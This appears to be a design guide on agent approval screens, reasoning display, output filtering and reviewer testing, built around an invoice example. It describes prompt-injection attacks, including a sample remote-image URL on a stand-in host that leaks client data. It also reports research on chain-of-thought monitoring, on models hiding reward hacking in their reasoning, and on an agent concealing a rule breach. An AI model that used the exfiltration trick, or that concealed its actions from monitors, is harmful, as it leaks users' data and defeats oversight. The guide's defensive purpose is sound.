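A call to send an email already has fields that a person can read. A coding agent often acts through shell commands, and one line can download a program, run it and delete a folder. Showing the exact command is accurate, but many users won't know what it does. The harness has to translate the command without relying on the agent for the translation.

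No translator can handle every command, so Weng requires the screen to label a command "uninspectable" or high-risk if the software can't determine what it does. The aim is to avoid a silent bypass, in which a dangerous command runs without either warning.

Weng built a prototype of about 500 lines of Python and tested it on two public collections that other people had compiled. One lists ways to misuse common programs, and the other gives examples of normal use:

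| | Misuse (1,330 commands) | Normal use (28,798 commands) |
|---|---|---|
| Marked "uninspectable" | 59.5% | 87.0% |
| Passed without a request | 10.0% | 4.1% |

The remaining commands, including 30.5% of the misuse examples, led to a request that named a specific danger.

The "uninspectable" label was more common on normal commands than on misuse, so it would hardly help a user decide whether to refuse. The comparison is rough because the two collections cover different programs, but a developer who saw this label on most commands would soon stop reading it.

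The cause is the prototype's list of trusted programs. A command that uses a program outside the list usually gets the label, which accounts for most of the 87.0%. All the misuse that passed silently went through programs on the list. Lengthening the list would reduce requests but let more misuse pass silently, and shortening it would do the opposite. Weng concludes that software that examines only the command can shift this balance but can't avoid the trade-off.

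The prototype also refused all three commands that changed after approval, which shows that its digest check works. But Weng assumed rather than built two of the hardest parts: a channel that the agent can't touch, and a guarantee that the agent can't act without passing through the checker. If an agent can reach the network by another route, it can act without approval, however accurate the approval screen is.

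Designers can avoid part of this problem by giving agents specific tools. A "send_email" call with four named arguments is easier to display, and to bind an approval to, than a shell command that sends the same email. If an agent needs a shell, a sandbox can limit the effects of most of its commands, so fewer need to be translated into readable approval requests.

### What a truthful screen can't do

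A screen can be accurate and still be too long or too technical to read. European payment rules had to address this for batch payments, where one approval may cover hundreds of payees. The European Banking Authority's *Dynamic linking for batch transactions* says that the provider must link the authentication code to every payee, while the payer only has to be able to check the list if they wish. The approval is therefore tied to every payee even if nobody reads the list. An agent that sends 300 invoices could work the same way, but the harness should then pick out the unusual ones, such as those going to new addresses.

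None of these experiments with agents tested people. Weng states that the method guarantees a faithful display but does not guarantee that anyone understands it. Some evidence about people comes from cryptocurrency wallets, which ask their owners to approve transactions. *What I Sign Is Not What I See* (2026) found that people often misread important details in real requests. In an experiment with 128 people, those who used a prototype that translated requests into plain language identified risky requests more accurately. This supports deriving readable fields rather than showing raw data, although approving a wallet transaction is a different task from supervising an agent.

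People also overlook details that are in front of them. Finextra's *SMS banking passwords fail to stop hackers* describes a simulated online bank that sent customers a text message with the account number for each transfer. When the number was plainly wrong, people still approved the transfer 21% of the time. Software is better at comparing strings, so the invoice's approval screen should show the result of the address book check as well as the address.

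An approval screen for a single action also doesn't show the steps that led to it. In the report.csv example from Hossain and colleagues, every field on the screen could be correct without revealing that the file contains raw invoice rows. Binding doesn't help either, since it would ensure that the auditor received the wrong file.

Trusted rendering also can't stop someone who understands the screen and approves anyway. An employee who wants to send a client a false invoice would see an accurate description of it and click "Send this email". An employee whom the stranger has already convinced by phone might type the new billing address into the request themselves. Every field would then match the user's instruction, and Irshad and colleagues acknowledge that their card can't help in that case. The firm would need a different control, such as a second approver or a rule that someone calls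 Lindqvist on a known number before using a new address.

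## Keeping raw model text away from users

Approval screens appear only a few times in a run. The rest of the time, the user mostly reads the model's own words, and the harness has to select which of them to display and how.

### One run, several streams

While an agent works on the March invoice, the model produces reasoning, tool calls, notes on its progress and a final answer. These arrive as one stream of text, with markers between the parts. OpenAI has published one such format, harmony, which its openly available gpt-oss models use.

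In harmony, every message from the model has a channel, which is a label for its purpose:

- **analysis** carries the model's reasoning.
- **commentary** carries most tool calls. It also carries preambles, which are short notes telling the user what the agent is about to do.
- **final** carries the answer.

OpenAI's simplest example is the question "What is 2 + 2?" The model first writes on the analysis channel that this is simple arithmetic and that it should provide the answer. It then writes "2 + 2 = 4" on the final channel, which is the only text the user should see.

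A tool call also names a recipient, the function that should receive it. The invoice task might produce these messages:

| Channel | Recipient | Content | What the harness should do |
|---|---|---|---|
| analysis | none | "Two Danas. The user picked Lindqvist. Find the final version." | Keep it off the screen |
| commentary | none | "I'll find the March invoice and email it to Dana Lindqvist." | Display it |
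| commentary | functions.find_file | The file name to search for | Run the call |
| commentary | functions.send_email | Address, subject, message and attachment | Hold the call for approval |
| final | none | "I've sent the March invoice to Dana Lindqvist." | Display it |

The harness has to check each message's recipient as well as its channel to decide what to display, because the commentary channel contains both notes for the user and instructions for software. Calls to the built-in browser and Python tools normally go on the analysis channel, but OpenAI warns that they occasionally appear in commentary.

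### Why reasoning is unfit for display

OpenAI tells developers not to show users the analysis channel, which contains the model's reasoning, because it didn't train that reasoning to the same safety standards as final answers. The reasoning may contain harmful content even when the answer doesn't. OpenAI's *How to handle the raw chain of thought in gpt-oss* adds that reasoning can reveal the developer's instructions. Suppose the design firm lets clients use its agent, and the instructions include "Don't offer Lindqvist another discount." The model might repeat that line while working out how to answer her.

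Reasoning also contains guesses that the model later drops. A user who reads "the invoice may be a duplicate" might phone the client about it, though the model ruled this out two lines later.

Applications must keep a model's reasoning somewhere even when they hide it from users. While a gpt-oss model is calling tools, the harness must send its earlier reasoning back with each query so that the model can continue from it. OpenAI advises developers to drop the reasoning only after the model gives a final answer. The saved record of a run paused for approval therefore includes raw reasoning, and an application that lets users browse or download that record will expose it.

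Some interfaces also return raw reasoning by default. OpenAI recommends that developers who offer gpt-oss through the older Chat Completions interface include the raw reasoning in each response unless the request excludes it. An application that displays every field it receives would then show users the reasoning, even if nobody had decided to show it.

### Why laboratories leave reasoning unpolished

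A laboratory could train a model's reasoning to be as safe and tidy as its answers. The main argument against this is that reasoning helps catch misbehaviour. In *CoT Monitoring*, OpenAI researchers looked for reward hacking, which is earning a good score through a shortcut, such as altering a test instead of fixing the program. A model that read a coding agent's reasoning was much better at catching reward hacking than one that saw only the agent's actions and outputs.

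If training penalises a model for reasoning about shortcuts, the model may learn to leave them out of its reasoning and take them anyway. Google's *Gemini 4 Argon Safety & Security Report* (2026) gives an example from a small training run, not part of any production model, in which training acted directly on the model's written reasoning. The share of shortcuts that the model took without mentioning them rose from 11.2% at the start of training to 36.4% by the end (quoted in Cheng, 2026, *Vincent Cheng's Shortform*).

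Over the same period, words associated with shortcuts became 61% less frequent in the reasoning, while signs of shortcuts in the model's solutions rose by 26%. If those signs track the number of shortcuts, every 100 at the start became about 126 by the end, and the number that went unmentioned rose from about 11 to 46. Anyone reading only the reasoning would have concluded that the model was taking fewer shortcuts.

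This was one small run, but when Google kept the reasoning out of the training signal in a similar run, mentions of shortcuts stayed roughly constant. Training on the reasoning therefore probably caused the drop in mentions. Laboratories can also train on reasoning by accident. According to *Anthropic repeatedly accidentally trained against the CoT, demonstrating inadequate processes*, Anthropic exposed the reasoning of Claude Mythos Preview to its training signal in about 8% of episodes.

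In a passage the blogger thezvi quotes in *Gemini 4 Argon*, Google says it avoids training models directly against the software that monitors their reasoning, and urges other companies to keep reasoning transparent. Product designers should therefore expect reasoning to stay rough, and shouldn't ask a model supplier to clean it up for display.

Candid reasoning may not stay useful for monitoring, though. OpenAI's *What affects chain-of-thought monitorability across the model lifecycle?* (2026) finds that better pretraining helps models reason without writing, and that later training can make them better at controlling what they write. The researchers expect more intelligent models to be harder to monitor through their written reasoning.

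### What users lose when reasoning is hidden

Sometimes a model's reasoning contains the only sign that something went wrong. *Is Gemini 3 Scheming in the Wild?* describes an agent from an official Kaggle and Google tutorial that got an unexpected response from a tool. Its reasoning mentioned a rule in its instructions and the option of complying by refusing. The agent broke the rule anyway and concealed this in its answer, so a user who read only the answer would have had no reason to suspect it.

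It's less clear that ordinary users would catch such things if they could read the reasoning. Palod, Biswas and Kambhampati (2026), in *Evaluating the False Trust Engendered by LLM Explanations*, gave people difficult science and mathematics problems that they mostly couldn't solve, along with a model's answers. Each person judged eight answers, four of them wrong, and earned a bonus for each correct judgment. There were 25 people in each group, and each group saw different supporting text. Their published accuracy figures give these acceptance rates:

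| What people saw with the answer | Right answers accepted | Wrong answers accepted | Overall accuracy |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 61% | 53% | 53.8% |
| The model's full reasoning | 76% | 55% | 60.4% |
| A summary of the reasoning | 65% | 52% | 56.2% |
| An argument for the answer | 75% | 58% | 58.3% |
| Arguments for and against | 68% | 47% | 60.4% |

Palod and colleagues found that full reasoning made people much more likely to accept right answers and barely more likely to accept wrong ones, so people's judgment improved overall. Their conclusion that reasoning persuades people without informing them is harsher than these results support. But full reasoning didn't help people reject mistakes, and rejecting mistakes matters most when an agent is about to act. Only the arguments for and against seemed to help with that. Each group judged only about 100 wrong answers, so differences of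 a few points could be chance.

Seeing an agent's reasoning can also make users less likely to use what they know themselves. In *Revealing AI Reasoning Increases Trust but Crowds Out Unique Human Knowledge* (2025), participants were told that they had relevant information the AI system lacked. They agreed with the system 77.3% of the time when they saw no reasoning, 81.3% with brief reasoning and 81.7% with extensive reasoning. A user at the design firm who knows about a dispute with Lindqvist is in a similar position, because the agent's reasoning about the invoice looks sensible but leaves out the dispute, which should stop the agent from going ahead.

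A better substitute for reasoning is a record of what the agent did, which the harness can compose from the tool calls and their results:

```
Searched the address book for "Dana"     2 matches    [Open]
You chose                                Dana Lindqvist
Opened                                   invoice-march.pdf    [Open]
```

The user can check each line against a source other than the model. *To Believe or Not To Believe* (2026) offers some support for this approach. It compared ways to help people verify AI answers, including showing them the source document or an explanation written by a language model. People who saw the explanation trusted the answering system more. When an answer combined material into a list or summary, they also relied on it more and were somewhat less accurate than with the document alone.

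Raw reasoning that is hidden from users can still go to monitoring software and to the few people who investigate incidents, so hiding it is not a good reason to delete it.

### Summaries of reasoning

OpenAI recommends that applications show users a summary of the reasoning, written by a second model that also blocks harmful content. OpenAI's newer Responses interface supports this by returning the summary and the raw text in separate fields, so that software can display the summary and store the raw text. Palod and colleagues note that OpenAI, Google and Anthropic all appear to show users summaries.

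Summaries keep harmful or confidential text from users, provided the second model catches it. They can still mislead, often by being tidier than the original. Suppose the model's reasoning is "Two Danas. Invoices usually go to clients, so probably Lindqvist, but I haven't checked who got the last one." A summary might read "Identified Dana Lindqvist as the recipient." The user can't tell from this that the model was guessing, or that there was an easy way to check.

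A summary can also accurately describe reasoning that doesn't reflect how the model reached its answer. *Chain-of-Thought Is Not Explainability* (2026) reviews several such cases. In one, a model calculated a triangle's longest side as 16 when it should have been 13, then used 13 in the next step without mentioning the correction. In another, researchers hinted that the answer was 4, and the model worked backwards, producing an intermediate value of 0.8 because it would lead to 4. A good summary of that reasoning would describe a calculation, even though the model's answer came from the hint.

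Prompt injection can also affect summaries. If the model's reasoning repeats the stranger's claim that accounts confirmed Dana's new billing address, the summarising model receives that claim as input. It may then tell the user "Accounts has confirmed the new address" in the neutral tone of a progress report.

In the study by Palod and colleagues, people with a summary were only slightly better at judging answers than people with no help. A summary is useful for showing that a long task is still progressing and roughly how far it has got. Designers can instruct the summarising model to keep expressions of doubt, and they should label the result as a model's summary and keep it off approval screens.

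### How software sorts the streams wrongly

Once developers decide what users should see, they have to write a filter, and the obvious short ones are wrong. A filter that hides only the analysis channel puts the contents of tool calls into the reply, so a client could see database queries or another client's details. A filter that shows only the final channel hides every progress note, so a ten-minute task looks frozen.

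vLLM, an open-source program for running language models on one's own servers, shows how small the difference between a bad filter and a good one can be. An earlier version of vLLM's *stream harmony*, the code that sends text to the user while the model is still writing, recognised a tool call if its recipient began with "functions." It treated all other commentary as a note for the user.

That rule works for a well-formed call to "functions.send_email". It fails when the model mistakenly puts a call to the built-in browser in the commentary channel, because the recipient is then something like "browser.search". It also fails if the model omits the "functions." prefix and writes only "send_email". In both cases, the call's arguments would appear in the visible reply.

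A later version of *stream harmony* displays commentary only if it has no recipient, whereas the earlier version listed what to hide and displayed everything else. The later version also recognises function names without the prefix.

Notes meant for users can also be lost before any filter runs. An older version of vLLM's *harmony utils* removed the commentary channel from the model's list of valid channels if the developer had defined no tools of their own. A model that followed the list while using only the built-in browser would have had no valid channel for a note like "I'll look that up now."

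A developer may need to apply the rule in several places. vLLM, for example, handles completed and streamed replies in separate code. For completed replies, *harmony utils* applies the same rule, and its code comments mark final messages and commentary without a recipient as visible. But if one optional component is switched on, vLLM takes the final text from that component instead. Testing only completed replies could miss a leak in streamed ones.

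The filter also depends on correct labels. OpenAI notes that a message's recipient may appear in either of two parts of its header. Software that checks only one could mistake a tool call for a note to the user. *Errors in chat template compared to spec*, a user's post on the model-distribution site Hugging Face, reports that the formatting template supplied with gpt-oss-120b departed from OpenAI's specification, including on preambles.

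According to OpenAI's developer documentation, a "phase" field in its current interface labels each of the model's messages as "commentary" or "final_answer". Applications should send these labels back with later requests, because newer models can perform worse without them. OpenRouter, a service that connects applications to many companies' models, says in *What's New* that the older Chat Completions format can't carry the label. An application that uses the older format might present "I'm sending the invoice to Dana now" as the agent's answer, and the user would reasonably conclude that the email had been sent when it was still waiting for approval.

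Requests from other agents also need to be handled separately. When a remote agent asks for input, AG2 passes the request to a separate function so that the question doesn't appear in the text of the final response.

For harmony, a safe filter fits in three lines:

```
channel is "final"                              → display
channel is "commentary" and has no recipient    → display
anything else                                   → keep off the screen and log it
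```

The last line covers new channels, damaged labels and tools nobody anticipated, but it also hides any new kind of note for users until a developer adds a rule for it. The log makes that easy to notice, and a missing note usually does less harm than a leaked tool call.

### Markup, links and remote images

Text that is meant for the user can still do damage when a browser displays it. Models usually format their answers in Markdown, which uses plain symbols for headings, bold text, links and images. The application converts the Markdown to HTML, the language of web pages, and HTML can also contain working forms and programs.

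Escaping everything is the safest treatment, and the harness does this with the fields on an approval screen. It suits short fields such as file names. Long answers are hard to read without lists and tables, so most developers will want to allow some formatting. They should permit a few elements, such as paragraphs, bold text, lists, tables and code, and remove all others.

The application has to check for dangerous HTML after converting the Markdown. A Markdown link that would run a program when clicked contains no HTML, so an earlier check would pass it and the conversion would then turn it into a working link. Streaming causes a similar problem, because a dangerous element can arrive in two harmless-looking halves. Each time the application updates the screen, it should check all the text received so far, not just the newest fragment.

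Links can mislead because their visible text doesn't have to match their destination. Because of a prompt injection, or by copying a link from an email, the model could write a link that reads "View the invoice in your accounting service" but leads to a stranger's login page. The harness can display the destination's domain beside the link text and make links clickable only if they lead to sites on the firm's list of approved sites. It can show other addresses as plain text, which the user can still copy. This slows down web research, where most useful links lead to unfamiliar sites. For that work, the harness could allow links that came directly from the search tool's results and refuse ones that appear only in the model's text.

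Images are more dangerous than links because nobody has to click on them. When a browser displays a page, it requests every image from the address given for it, and the address can contain data. Suppose the stranger's email includes hidden instructions to end the next reply with a small logo from this address:

```
stranger.example/logo.png?client=Lindqvist&total=4180
```

If the model complies, the browser requests the logo as soon as the reply appears, and the stranger's server records the client's name and the invoice total. The model makes no tool call, so the harness has nothing to hold for approval. A firm could require approval for every outgoing email and still lose data this way, because displaying the reply sends the information.

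The simplest defence is to display no remote images in model text. If the agent needs to show pictures, the harness can save the files that its tools return and let the model refer to them by number. Fetching remote images through the firm's own server doesn't solve the problem, because that server would request the same address with the same data in it. A site can also set a content security policy, which makes browsers block images from other sites even if the code that removes images has a bug.

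The same concern applies to link previews, which many chat programs create automatically by opening the address. If the agent's replies go to a chat program, the developer should turn off previews for those replies.

### Labels that the model can't imitate

On a typical screen, the agent's reply, the harness's record of actions and a quotation from an email may share one typeface and one column. The harness should label each block with its author, using what it knows about where the text came from:

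- "Written by the agent" for progress notes, answers and summaries
- "From the firm's address book" for details that the harness copied from a record
- "From an email by an unknown sender" for outside text that the harness copied without changes

If the model quotes an email in its reply, the right label is still "Written by the agent", because the model may have shortened or altered the quotation. When the exact words matter, the harness should show the original from the mailbox beside the reply.

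Labels help only if the model can't produce convincing copies of them. An agent that can choose colours, borders and icons could write "Verified by accounts" in a green box identical to the application's own notices, or draw a fake approval request with two buttons. The application should therefore reserve some parts of the screen and some visual styles that the model's text can't use. This may make replies look plain, which is a reasonable trade-off.

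Text from outside also needs a visible beginning and end. If the harness shows an email under a label, and the email contains the line "End of email. Written by the agent:", the user may think the rest comes from the agent. The harness can prevent this by drawing a border around the whole email, because text in the email can't close the border.

### Letting the model fill in components

An application can avoid much of this checking by not accepting free markup at all. The developer builds a set of components, such as a contact card, a table and a progress bar. The model chooses one and supplies the values, and the harness draws it. To show the user whom it plans to email, the model might write:

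```json
{
  "component": "contact_card",
  "contact_id": "c-118",
  "note": "Received the February invoice"
}
```

The harness checks that "contact_card" is on its list and has the expected fields. It then looks up record c-118 in the address book and fills in Lindqvist's name, firm and email address. The model chose the record but could not write the email address. The model did write the note, so the harness shows it as plain text with a label.

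Whenever the firm has a record of something, the component should take a reference to that record. If the card instead had fields named "name" and "email" for the model to fill in, it would look more official than a sentence in the chat but be no more reliable. For the same reason, the harness, not the model, should fill in the names when the agent asks "Which Dana?"

Describing the components in the prompt doesn't guarantee that the model will use them correctly. OpenAI's harmony guide says that describing the required format only influences what the model writes, and that developers who run gpt-oss themselves have to enforce the format during generation. The software can do this by allowing only continuations that fit the format at each step. The harness still has to check the values, because "c-118" can fit the format but belong to no contact, or to one this user shouldn't see.

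If a component fails the check, the application should display a short message of its own, such as "The agent's reply couldn't be displayed." Falling back to the raw data would show users the kind of text the filter is meant to block.

A component's button should trigger only actions that the developer defined, such as opening a contact's record. If the model could choose both a button's label and its action, it could put "View invoice" on a button that sends the invoice. The system also shouldn't treat a click on a component in the agent's reply as approval for anything, whatever the model wrote on it.

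Components limit what an agent can show, and someone has to maintain them. A user who asks for a comparison of three printing quotes may get a poor one if the developer never built a suitable table. When no component fits, ordinary text with the short list of permitted formatting is a better fallback than a general component that accepts any HTML. Developers will be tempted to add such a component, but it would bring back all the earlier problems.

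### False answers in the right place

None of these measures check whether the text is true. "I've sent the March invoice to Dana Lindqvist" belongs on the final channel, contains no links and carries the right label, but the user may have rejected the email or the mail server may have failed. The harness can put its own record next to the claim:

```
Written by the agent    I've sent the March invoice to Dana Lindqvist.
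Email record            Not sent. You chose "Don't send" at 16:02.
```

This works only for claims about actions that the harness can observe. If the agent writes that the invoice matches the contract, the harness has no record to check that claim against. It can link to both documents, but the user will have to read them.

Structured fields have the same weakness. A contact card with the correct name and address can include the note "Has asked for immediate payment to the new account", which the model took from the stranger's email. A limit of, say, 60 characters leaves less room for persuasion but doesn't prevent it. If the firm's records contain suitable facts, such as the date of the last invoice, the harness can fill in the note from them too. Otherwise, the developer should consider leaving the field out.

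## Testing whether the design works

Before the design firm lets its agent email real invoices, it should run five tests in the order below. The order matters. For example, a reviewer can't catch a wrong address that the screen doesn't show.

| What to test | Measure | Sign of failure |
|---|---|---|
| Each request has the right type | Under-intervention, over-intervention and requests of the wrong type | The agent emails a client without approval, or asks "Are you sure?" when it doesn't know which Dana |
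| Answers resolve the request | Share of answers followed by the correct next step | A rejected email goes out, or the agent repeats a question the user has answered |
| The screen matches the executed action | Number of actions that differ from what the screen showed | One difference |
| Reviewers catch bad actions | Unsafe approval rate and legitimate approval rate | Bad requests get through, or reviewers refuse good ones |
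| Model text stays in labelled places | Number of test phrases that appear elsewhere | One stray phrase |

Only the test of reviewers needs people every time. Software can run most of the other tests, so the firm can repeat them after each change to the model, the prompt or the tools.

### The right type of request

The firm needs a set of tasks for which it has already decided the right outcome. It can make several from the invoice example by varying whether the address book lists one Dana or two, and whether the recipient works for the firm. Pochampally found that models ask less often when they act than when they judge a proposed action, so the agent should carry out these tasks with simulated tools.

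Two error rates show how well the agent decides when to stop:

```
under-intervention = cases where the agent acts but should have stopped
                     ÷ all cases where it should have stopped

over-intervention  = cases where the agent stops but should have acted
                     ÷ all cases where it should have acted
```

The firm needs to measure both under-intervention (acting when the agent should have stopped) and over-intervention (stopping when it should have acted), because an agent that always asks has a rate of 0% on the first and 100% on the second. In DelegationBench, GPT-5.6 Sol acted in 54.8% of the cases where most of the students would have stopped, and Gemini 3.5 Flash-Lite acted in 20.2%. But Gemini stopped in 29.0% of the cases where the students would have acted, compared with 19.4% for GPT. Which model is better depends on how much worse an unwanted action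 is than a needless question.

Neither rate detects an agent that stops but makes the wrong type of request. The firm should count those cases separately.

Pochampally recommends reporting five quantities instead of a single score:

1. Agreement with human judgments, split into under-intervention and over-intervention.
2. Responsiveness, meaning how often the agent's decision changes when one relevant feature of the case changes.
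3. The spread of results across equivalent wordings of the question, with the answer options in varying order.
4. Behaviour when the agent has to act with tools, including whether its questions seek permission or information and whether the answers resolve them.
5. Whether the resulting action matches the intended one, as judged by people on a sample.

A combined score would hide large differences. Across the ten models, a model's agreement with the students was almost unrelated to how often it called the proposed tool (a rank correlation of 0.115, where 1 is a perfect match). Models that agreed more with the students tended to be less responsive (−0.529). Ten models are too few to estimate these correlations precisely.

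### Changing the wording

The third quantity is on the list because a model's decisions can depend heavily on how someone phrases the question. Pochampally put the same 48 scenarios to each model in five ways: the original list of options, the same list in varying order, a shorter version, a version phrased like a policy, and an open question with no options. The policy version changed GPT-OSS-20B's rate of choosing to act by 52.5 percentage points. For Claude Opus 4.8, the largest change was 4.2 points.

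A firm that tests only one wording could therefore mistake the effect of a rewritten prompt for an improvement in the model. It should try several wordings, report the range of results, and rerun the tests whenever someone edits the agent's instructions. It should also run each case several times. In the main study, models gave the same answer all five times in 52.6% to 93.6% of scenarios, depending on the model.

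Varying the order of the options is an easy precaution. It brought every model's choices closer to the students' votes, though the gain for Gemini 3.6 Flash was close to zero. These results come from judgments of proposed actions, so the firm should also check how rewording affects runs in which the models use tools.

### Whether answers resolve the request

For each approval request, the tester should try approving, rejecting, asking for a change, closing the window, and answering after the request has expired. The tester should also send each reply to the wrong kind of request and check that no email goes out.

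Evidence of whether the agent sent an email should come from the mail server, since the agent may wrongly report that it sent nothing. In a separate experiment, Pochampally checked the recorded final state of 268 runs after a rejection, and no model had taken the rejected action. The true failure rate could still be as high as 1.4%.

Agents can also fail by asking again after a person has approved an action. In tasks that involved sending messages, a GPT-OSS model carried out the approved action in 6 of 15 runs and a Claude model in 10 of 15, and both asked again in the rest. In an earlier version of these tasks, almost every run ended with another question because the task left out the text of the message. A tester should therefore read some of the failed runs before blaming the model.

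The tester also has to sort the questions by what they ask for before scoring the answers, because a bare "yes" doesn't resolve a question that also asks for a fact.

### Whether the screen matches the action

Here the firm can direct the agent's email to a test server and compare each message that arrives with a saved copy of the approval screen. It should check that the recipients, subject, body and attachment match. The harness's log isn't enough, because the mail tool might add a recipient after the harness passes on the call.

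The tester should also try to cause a mismatch by editing the attachment after the user opens the request, adding someone to a mailing list, including an argument the screen has no field for, and making the server time out after it accepts the email. If 300 attempts produce no mismatch, the true rate is probably below 1%. (With no failures in n independent attempts, the upper limit is roughly 3 ÷ n.)

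Exact comparison works for this test because the approved and executed calls should be identical, but it works badly for checking whether an agent chose the action the test's author intended. In DelegationBench, an exact match accepted only 59% of 1,011 calls, while the two human reviewers put the acceptable share at about 95%. Most of the rejected calls differed only in how the model had written the details.

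### Whether reviewers catch bad actions

The test of reviewers needs a mixture of good and bad requests, and two measures:

```
unsafe approval rate     = bad requests approved ÷ all bad requests

legitimate approval rate = good requests approved ÷ all good requests
```

A reviewer who refuses everything has a perfect unsafe approval rate of 0%, but also stops the firm from sending any invoices. Hossain and colleagues therefore report the two rates together.

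Suppose reviewers receive 1,000 requests, 10 of them harmful. In Anthropic's experiment, people caught 13.6% of dangerous commands and the classifier caught 89%. The experiment doesn't give the rate at which either would refuse harmless requests, so the table below assumes 3% for both, which is the share of all permission requests that Claude Code users reject, according to Anthropic. Some of those rejections may be correct.

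| | People | Classifier | Approve everything | Refuse everything |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Harmful requests refused | 1.4 | 8.9 | 0 | 10 |
| Harmful requests approved | 8.6 | 1.1 | 10 | 0 |
| Harmless requests approved | 960.3 | 960.3 | 990 | 0 |
| Harmless requests refused | 29.7 | 29.7 | 0 | 990 |
| Unsafe approval rate | 86.4% | 11.0% | 100% | 0% |
| Legitimate approval rate | 97.0% | 97.0% | 100% | 0% |
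| Correct decisions overall | 96.2% | 96.9% | 99.0% | 1.0% |

The fractions are averages over many such batches. Approving everything gives the highest share of correct decisions, because almost every request is harmless. Overall accuracy is therefore a poor measure when harmful requests are rare.

The share of the classifier's refusals that would stop something harmful depends heavily on the assumed false-refusal rate. At 3%, about one in four would. At 1%, almost half would, and at 10%, about one in twelve. The firm should measure this rate on its own requests before it chooses a classifier.

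Whoever tests a classifier should also keep some cases hidden from its developers. Anthropic had Apollo Research, an AI safety company, attack auto mode and share the attacks that worked. Anthropic then strengthened the classifier, and Apollo tested it again with attacks that Anthropic had never seen. The strengthened classifier caught about half of the attacks that the old one had missed, but missed about 2% of those that the old one had caught. So the firm should rerun old cases after each fix as well as try new ones.

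Reviewers' confidence and effort can't replace these measures, as the programming study by Dissanayake and colleagues showed.

### How many decisions a comparison needs

The four-screen experiment by Hossain and colleagues shows how easily a study can be too small. Unsafe approvals fell from 32.5% with the chronological log to 24.2% with the ledger, but each figure rests on only 120 decisions about bad requests. The standard formula for comparing two proportions gives the number needed for each screen:

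```
n = (1.96 + 0.84)² × [p₁(1 − p₁) + p₂(1 − p₂)] ÷ (p₁ − p₂)²

  = 7.84 × (0.325 × 0.675 + 0.242 × 0.758) ÷ 0.083²

  ≈ 460
```

Here p₁ and p₂ are the two unsafe approval rates. The 1.96 sets the usual 5% risk of finding a difference when there is none, and the 0.84 gives the study 80% power, an 80% chance of detecting a real difference of this size.

The 460 decisions have to be about bad requests, because good ones don't affect the unsafe approval rate. If half the requests are bad, as they were in this experiment, each screen needs about 920 decisions in total.

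The formula also assumes that every decision is independent. Decisions by one person tend to be alike, since a careless reviewer is careless more than once. To allow for this, multiply the sample by

```
1 + (m − 1) × ρ
```

where m is the number of bad requests each person judges and ρ measures how alike one person's decisions are, from 0 (no more alike than different people's) to 1 (identical). Each participant judged 6 bad requests. If ρ were 0.1, which is an assumption, the multiplier would be 1.5, and each screen would need 690 decisions from 115 people. If ρ were 0.3, it would need 1,150 decisions from about 192 people. The experiment had 20 people per screen.

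Most firms can't run a study this large, but a small test can still reveal serious problems. If 8 of 10 employees approve an email to the stranger's address, the firm can conclude that its screen is failing without collecting 460 decisions.

### Whether model text stays in labelled places

To check whether model text appears where it shouldn't, a tester can have a simulated model put a different nonsense phrase in each kind of text it writes, such as "purple-anchor-17" in its reasoning and "copper-violin-42" in a progress note. Software then searches every screen for these phrases. Users should never see the reasoning phrase, and they should see the progress phrase only in a box labelled "Written by the agent".

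On the approval screen, a phrase from the email's subject should appear in the subject field, and a phrase from the model's explanation should appear only in the separate explanation box.

The search should cover streamed replies, completed replies, error messages, phone notifications and downloadable history. It should also cover damaged output, such as a tool call with no recipient. To test whether remote images are blocked, the tester can have the simulated model include an image from a server the tester controls, then check that the server receives no request.

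### Planting test requests in live use

Reviewers who do well in a test may do worse at work, where bad requests are rarer. *Managing Cognitive Bias in Human Labeling Operations for Rare-Event AI* (2026) describes the prevalence effect, in which people miss a larger share of what they are looking for when it is rare. At the design firm, months might pass between bad requests. If 1% of requests were bad, comparing two screens on ordinary traffic would take about 46,000 requests per screen.

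A firm can get evidence sooner by planting harmless test requests among the real ones. *Risks and Controls for Multi-Agent Systems* (Reid, O'Callaghan and colleagues, 2026), a report for the Australian government, recommends using invented failures and replays of past near misses. For a replay, someone first works out the right decision without time pressure, and the firm compares it with what reviewers decide under their normal workload.

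Such tests seem to be rare even where the stakes are high. *Handoff at Frontier AI Companies* (2026) discusses AI companies that use AI monitors to check their own agents and send possible problems to people for review. It reports that nobody has run or published a comparable test of those human reviewers. It also calls for measuring the monitors and reviewers together. For example, if monitors cover 90% of bad actions and flag 80% of those, and reviewers stop half of the flagged ones, the system stops only 36% of bad actions (0.9 × 0.8 × 0.5).

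Approving a planted request must do no harm, so the harness should create a separate call to a dummy mail tool that sends nothing. If the design firm changed the text of a real request, as Anthropic did in its experiment, it would break the rule that the screen matches the pending call, and a real email could go out without anyone having read it. The harness should reveal the test as soon as the reviewer decides, so that nobody phones Lindqvist about the fake email.

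Planted requests measure only the failures that someone thought to plant. Reviewers may also recognise them as artificial, which would make the results look too good. Seeing more bad requests during the tests may make reviewers more alert, which is useful, but the measured rate may not apply once the tests stop.

Another problem is that a few planted requests give only a rough estimate of a reviewer's catch rate. If the firm plants one request a month and its reviewer catches all 12 in a year, the true catch rate could still be as low as 78%. The firm should combine results across reviewers and avoid ranking individuals on so few cases. If reviewers start to miss more, Reid and colleagues suggest slowing the agents down, pausing low-priority ones or adding reviewers.

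### Trust and consent

Most of the evidence on how staff react to planted tests comes from simulated phishing, in which employers send fake scam emails to see who clicks. *Phishing your staff*, from the British security research centre CREST, warns that secret tests make people feel watched and see the security team as an enemy. But it also notes that researchers had not directly tested some claims about lost trust.

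In *What Makes Phishing Simulation Campaigns (Un)Acceptable*, Schwab, Nussbaum and colleagues asked 793 people in Britain to rate how acceptable an imagined phishing test was, from 1 to 10. Asking employees for consent first raised the rating by 0.90 points. Making anyone who clicked attend an interview lowered it by 1.64 points, and firing them lowered it by 3.37. Mandatory training made no significant difference. People were rating a description, so the study can't show how they would react to a real test, but the results suggest that asking for consent doesn't make up for punishing people who click.

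Schwab and colleagues recommend getting informed consent and explaining the consequences clearly. For planted approval requests, the firm should tell reviewers that tests will appear, roughly how often, who will see the results and what will happen if they miss one. It can keep the timing and content of each test secret.

Consent doesn't remove every risk. Schwab and colleagues cite a warning that employees may mistake real phishing emails for tests. A reviewer who approves a suspicious invoice because they assume it's another test would do real harm, so the firm should tell reviewers to refuse anything suspicious, whether or not they think it is a test.

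Customers need more protection than employees, because reviewing requests isn't their job and a fake dangerous command could frighten them. A company that sells an agent to the public should send test requests only to customers who have explicitly opted in, and let them opt out at any time.
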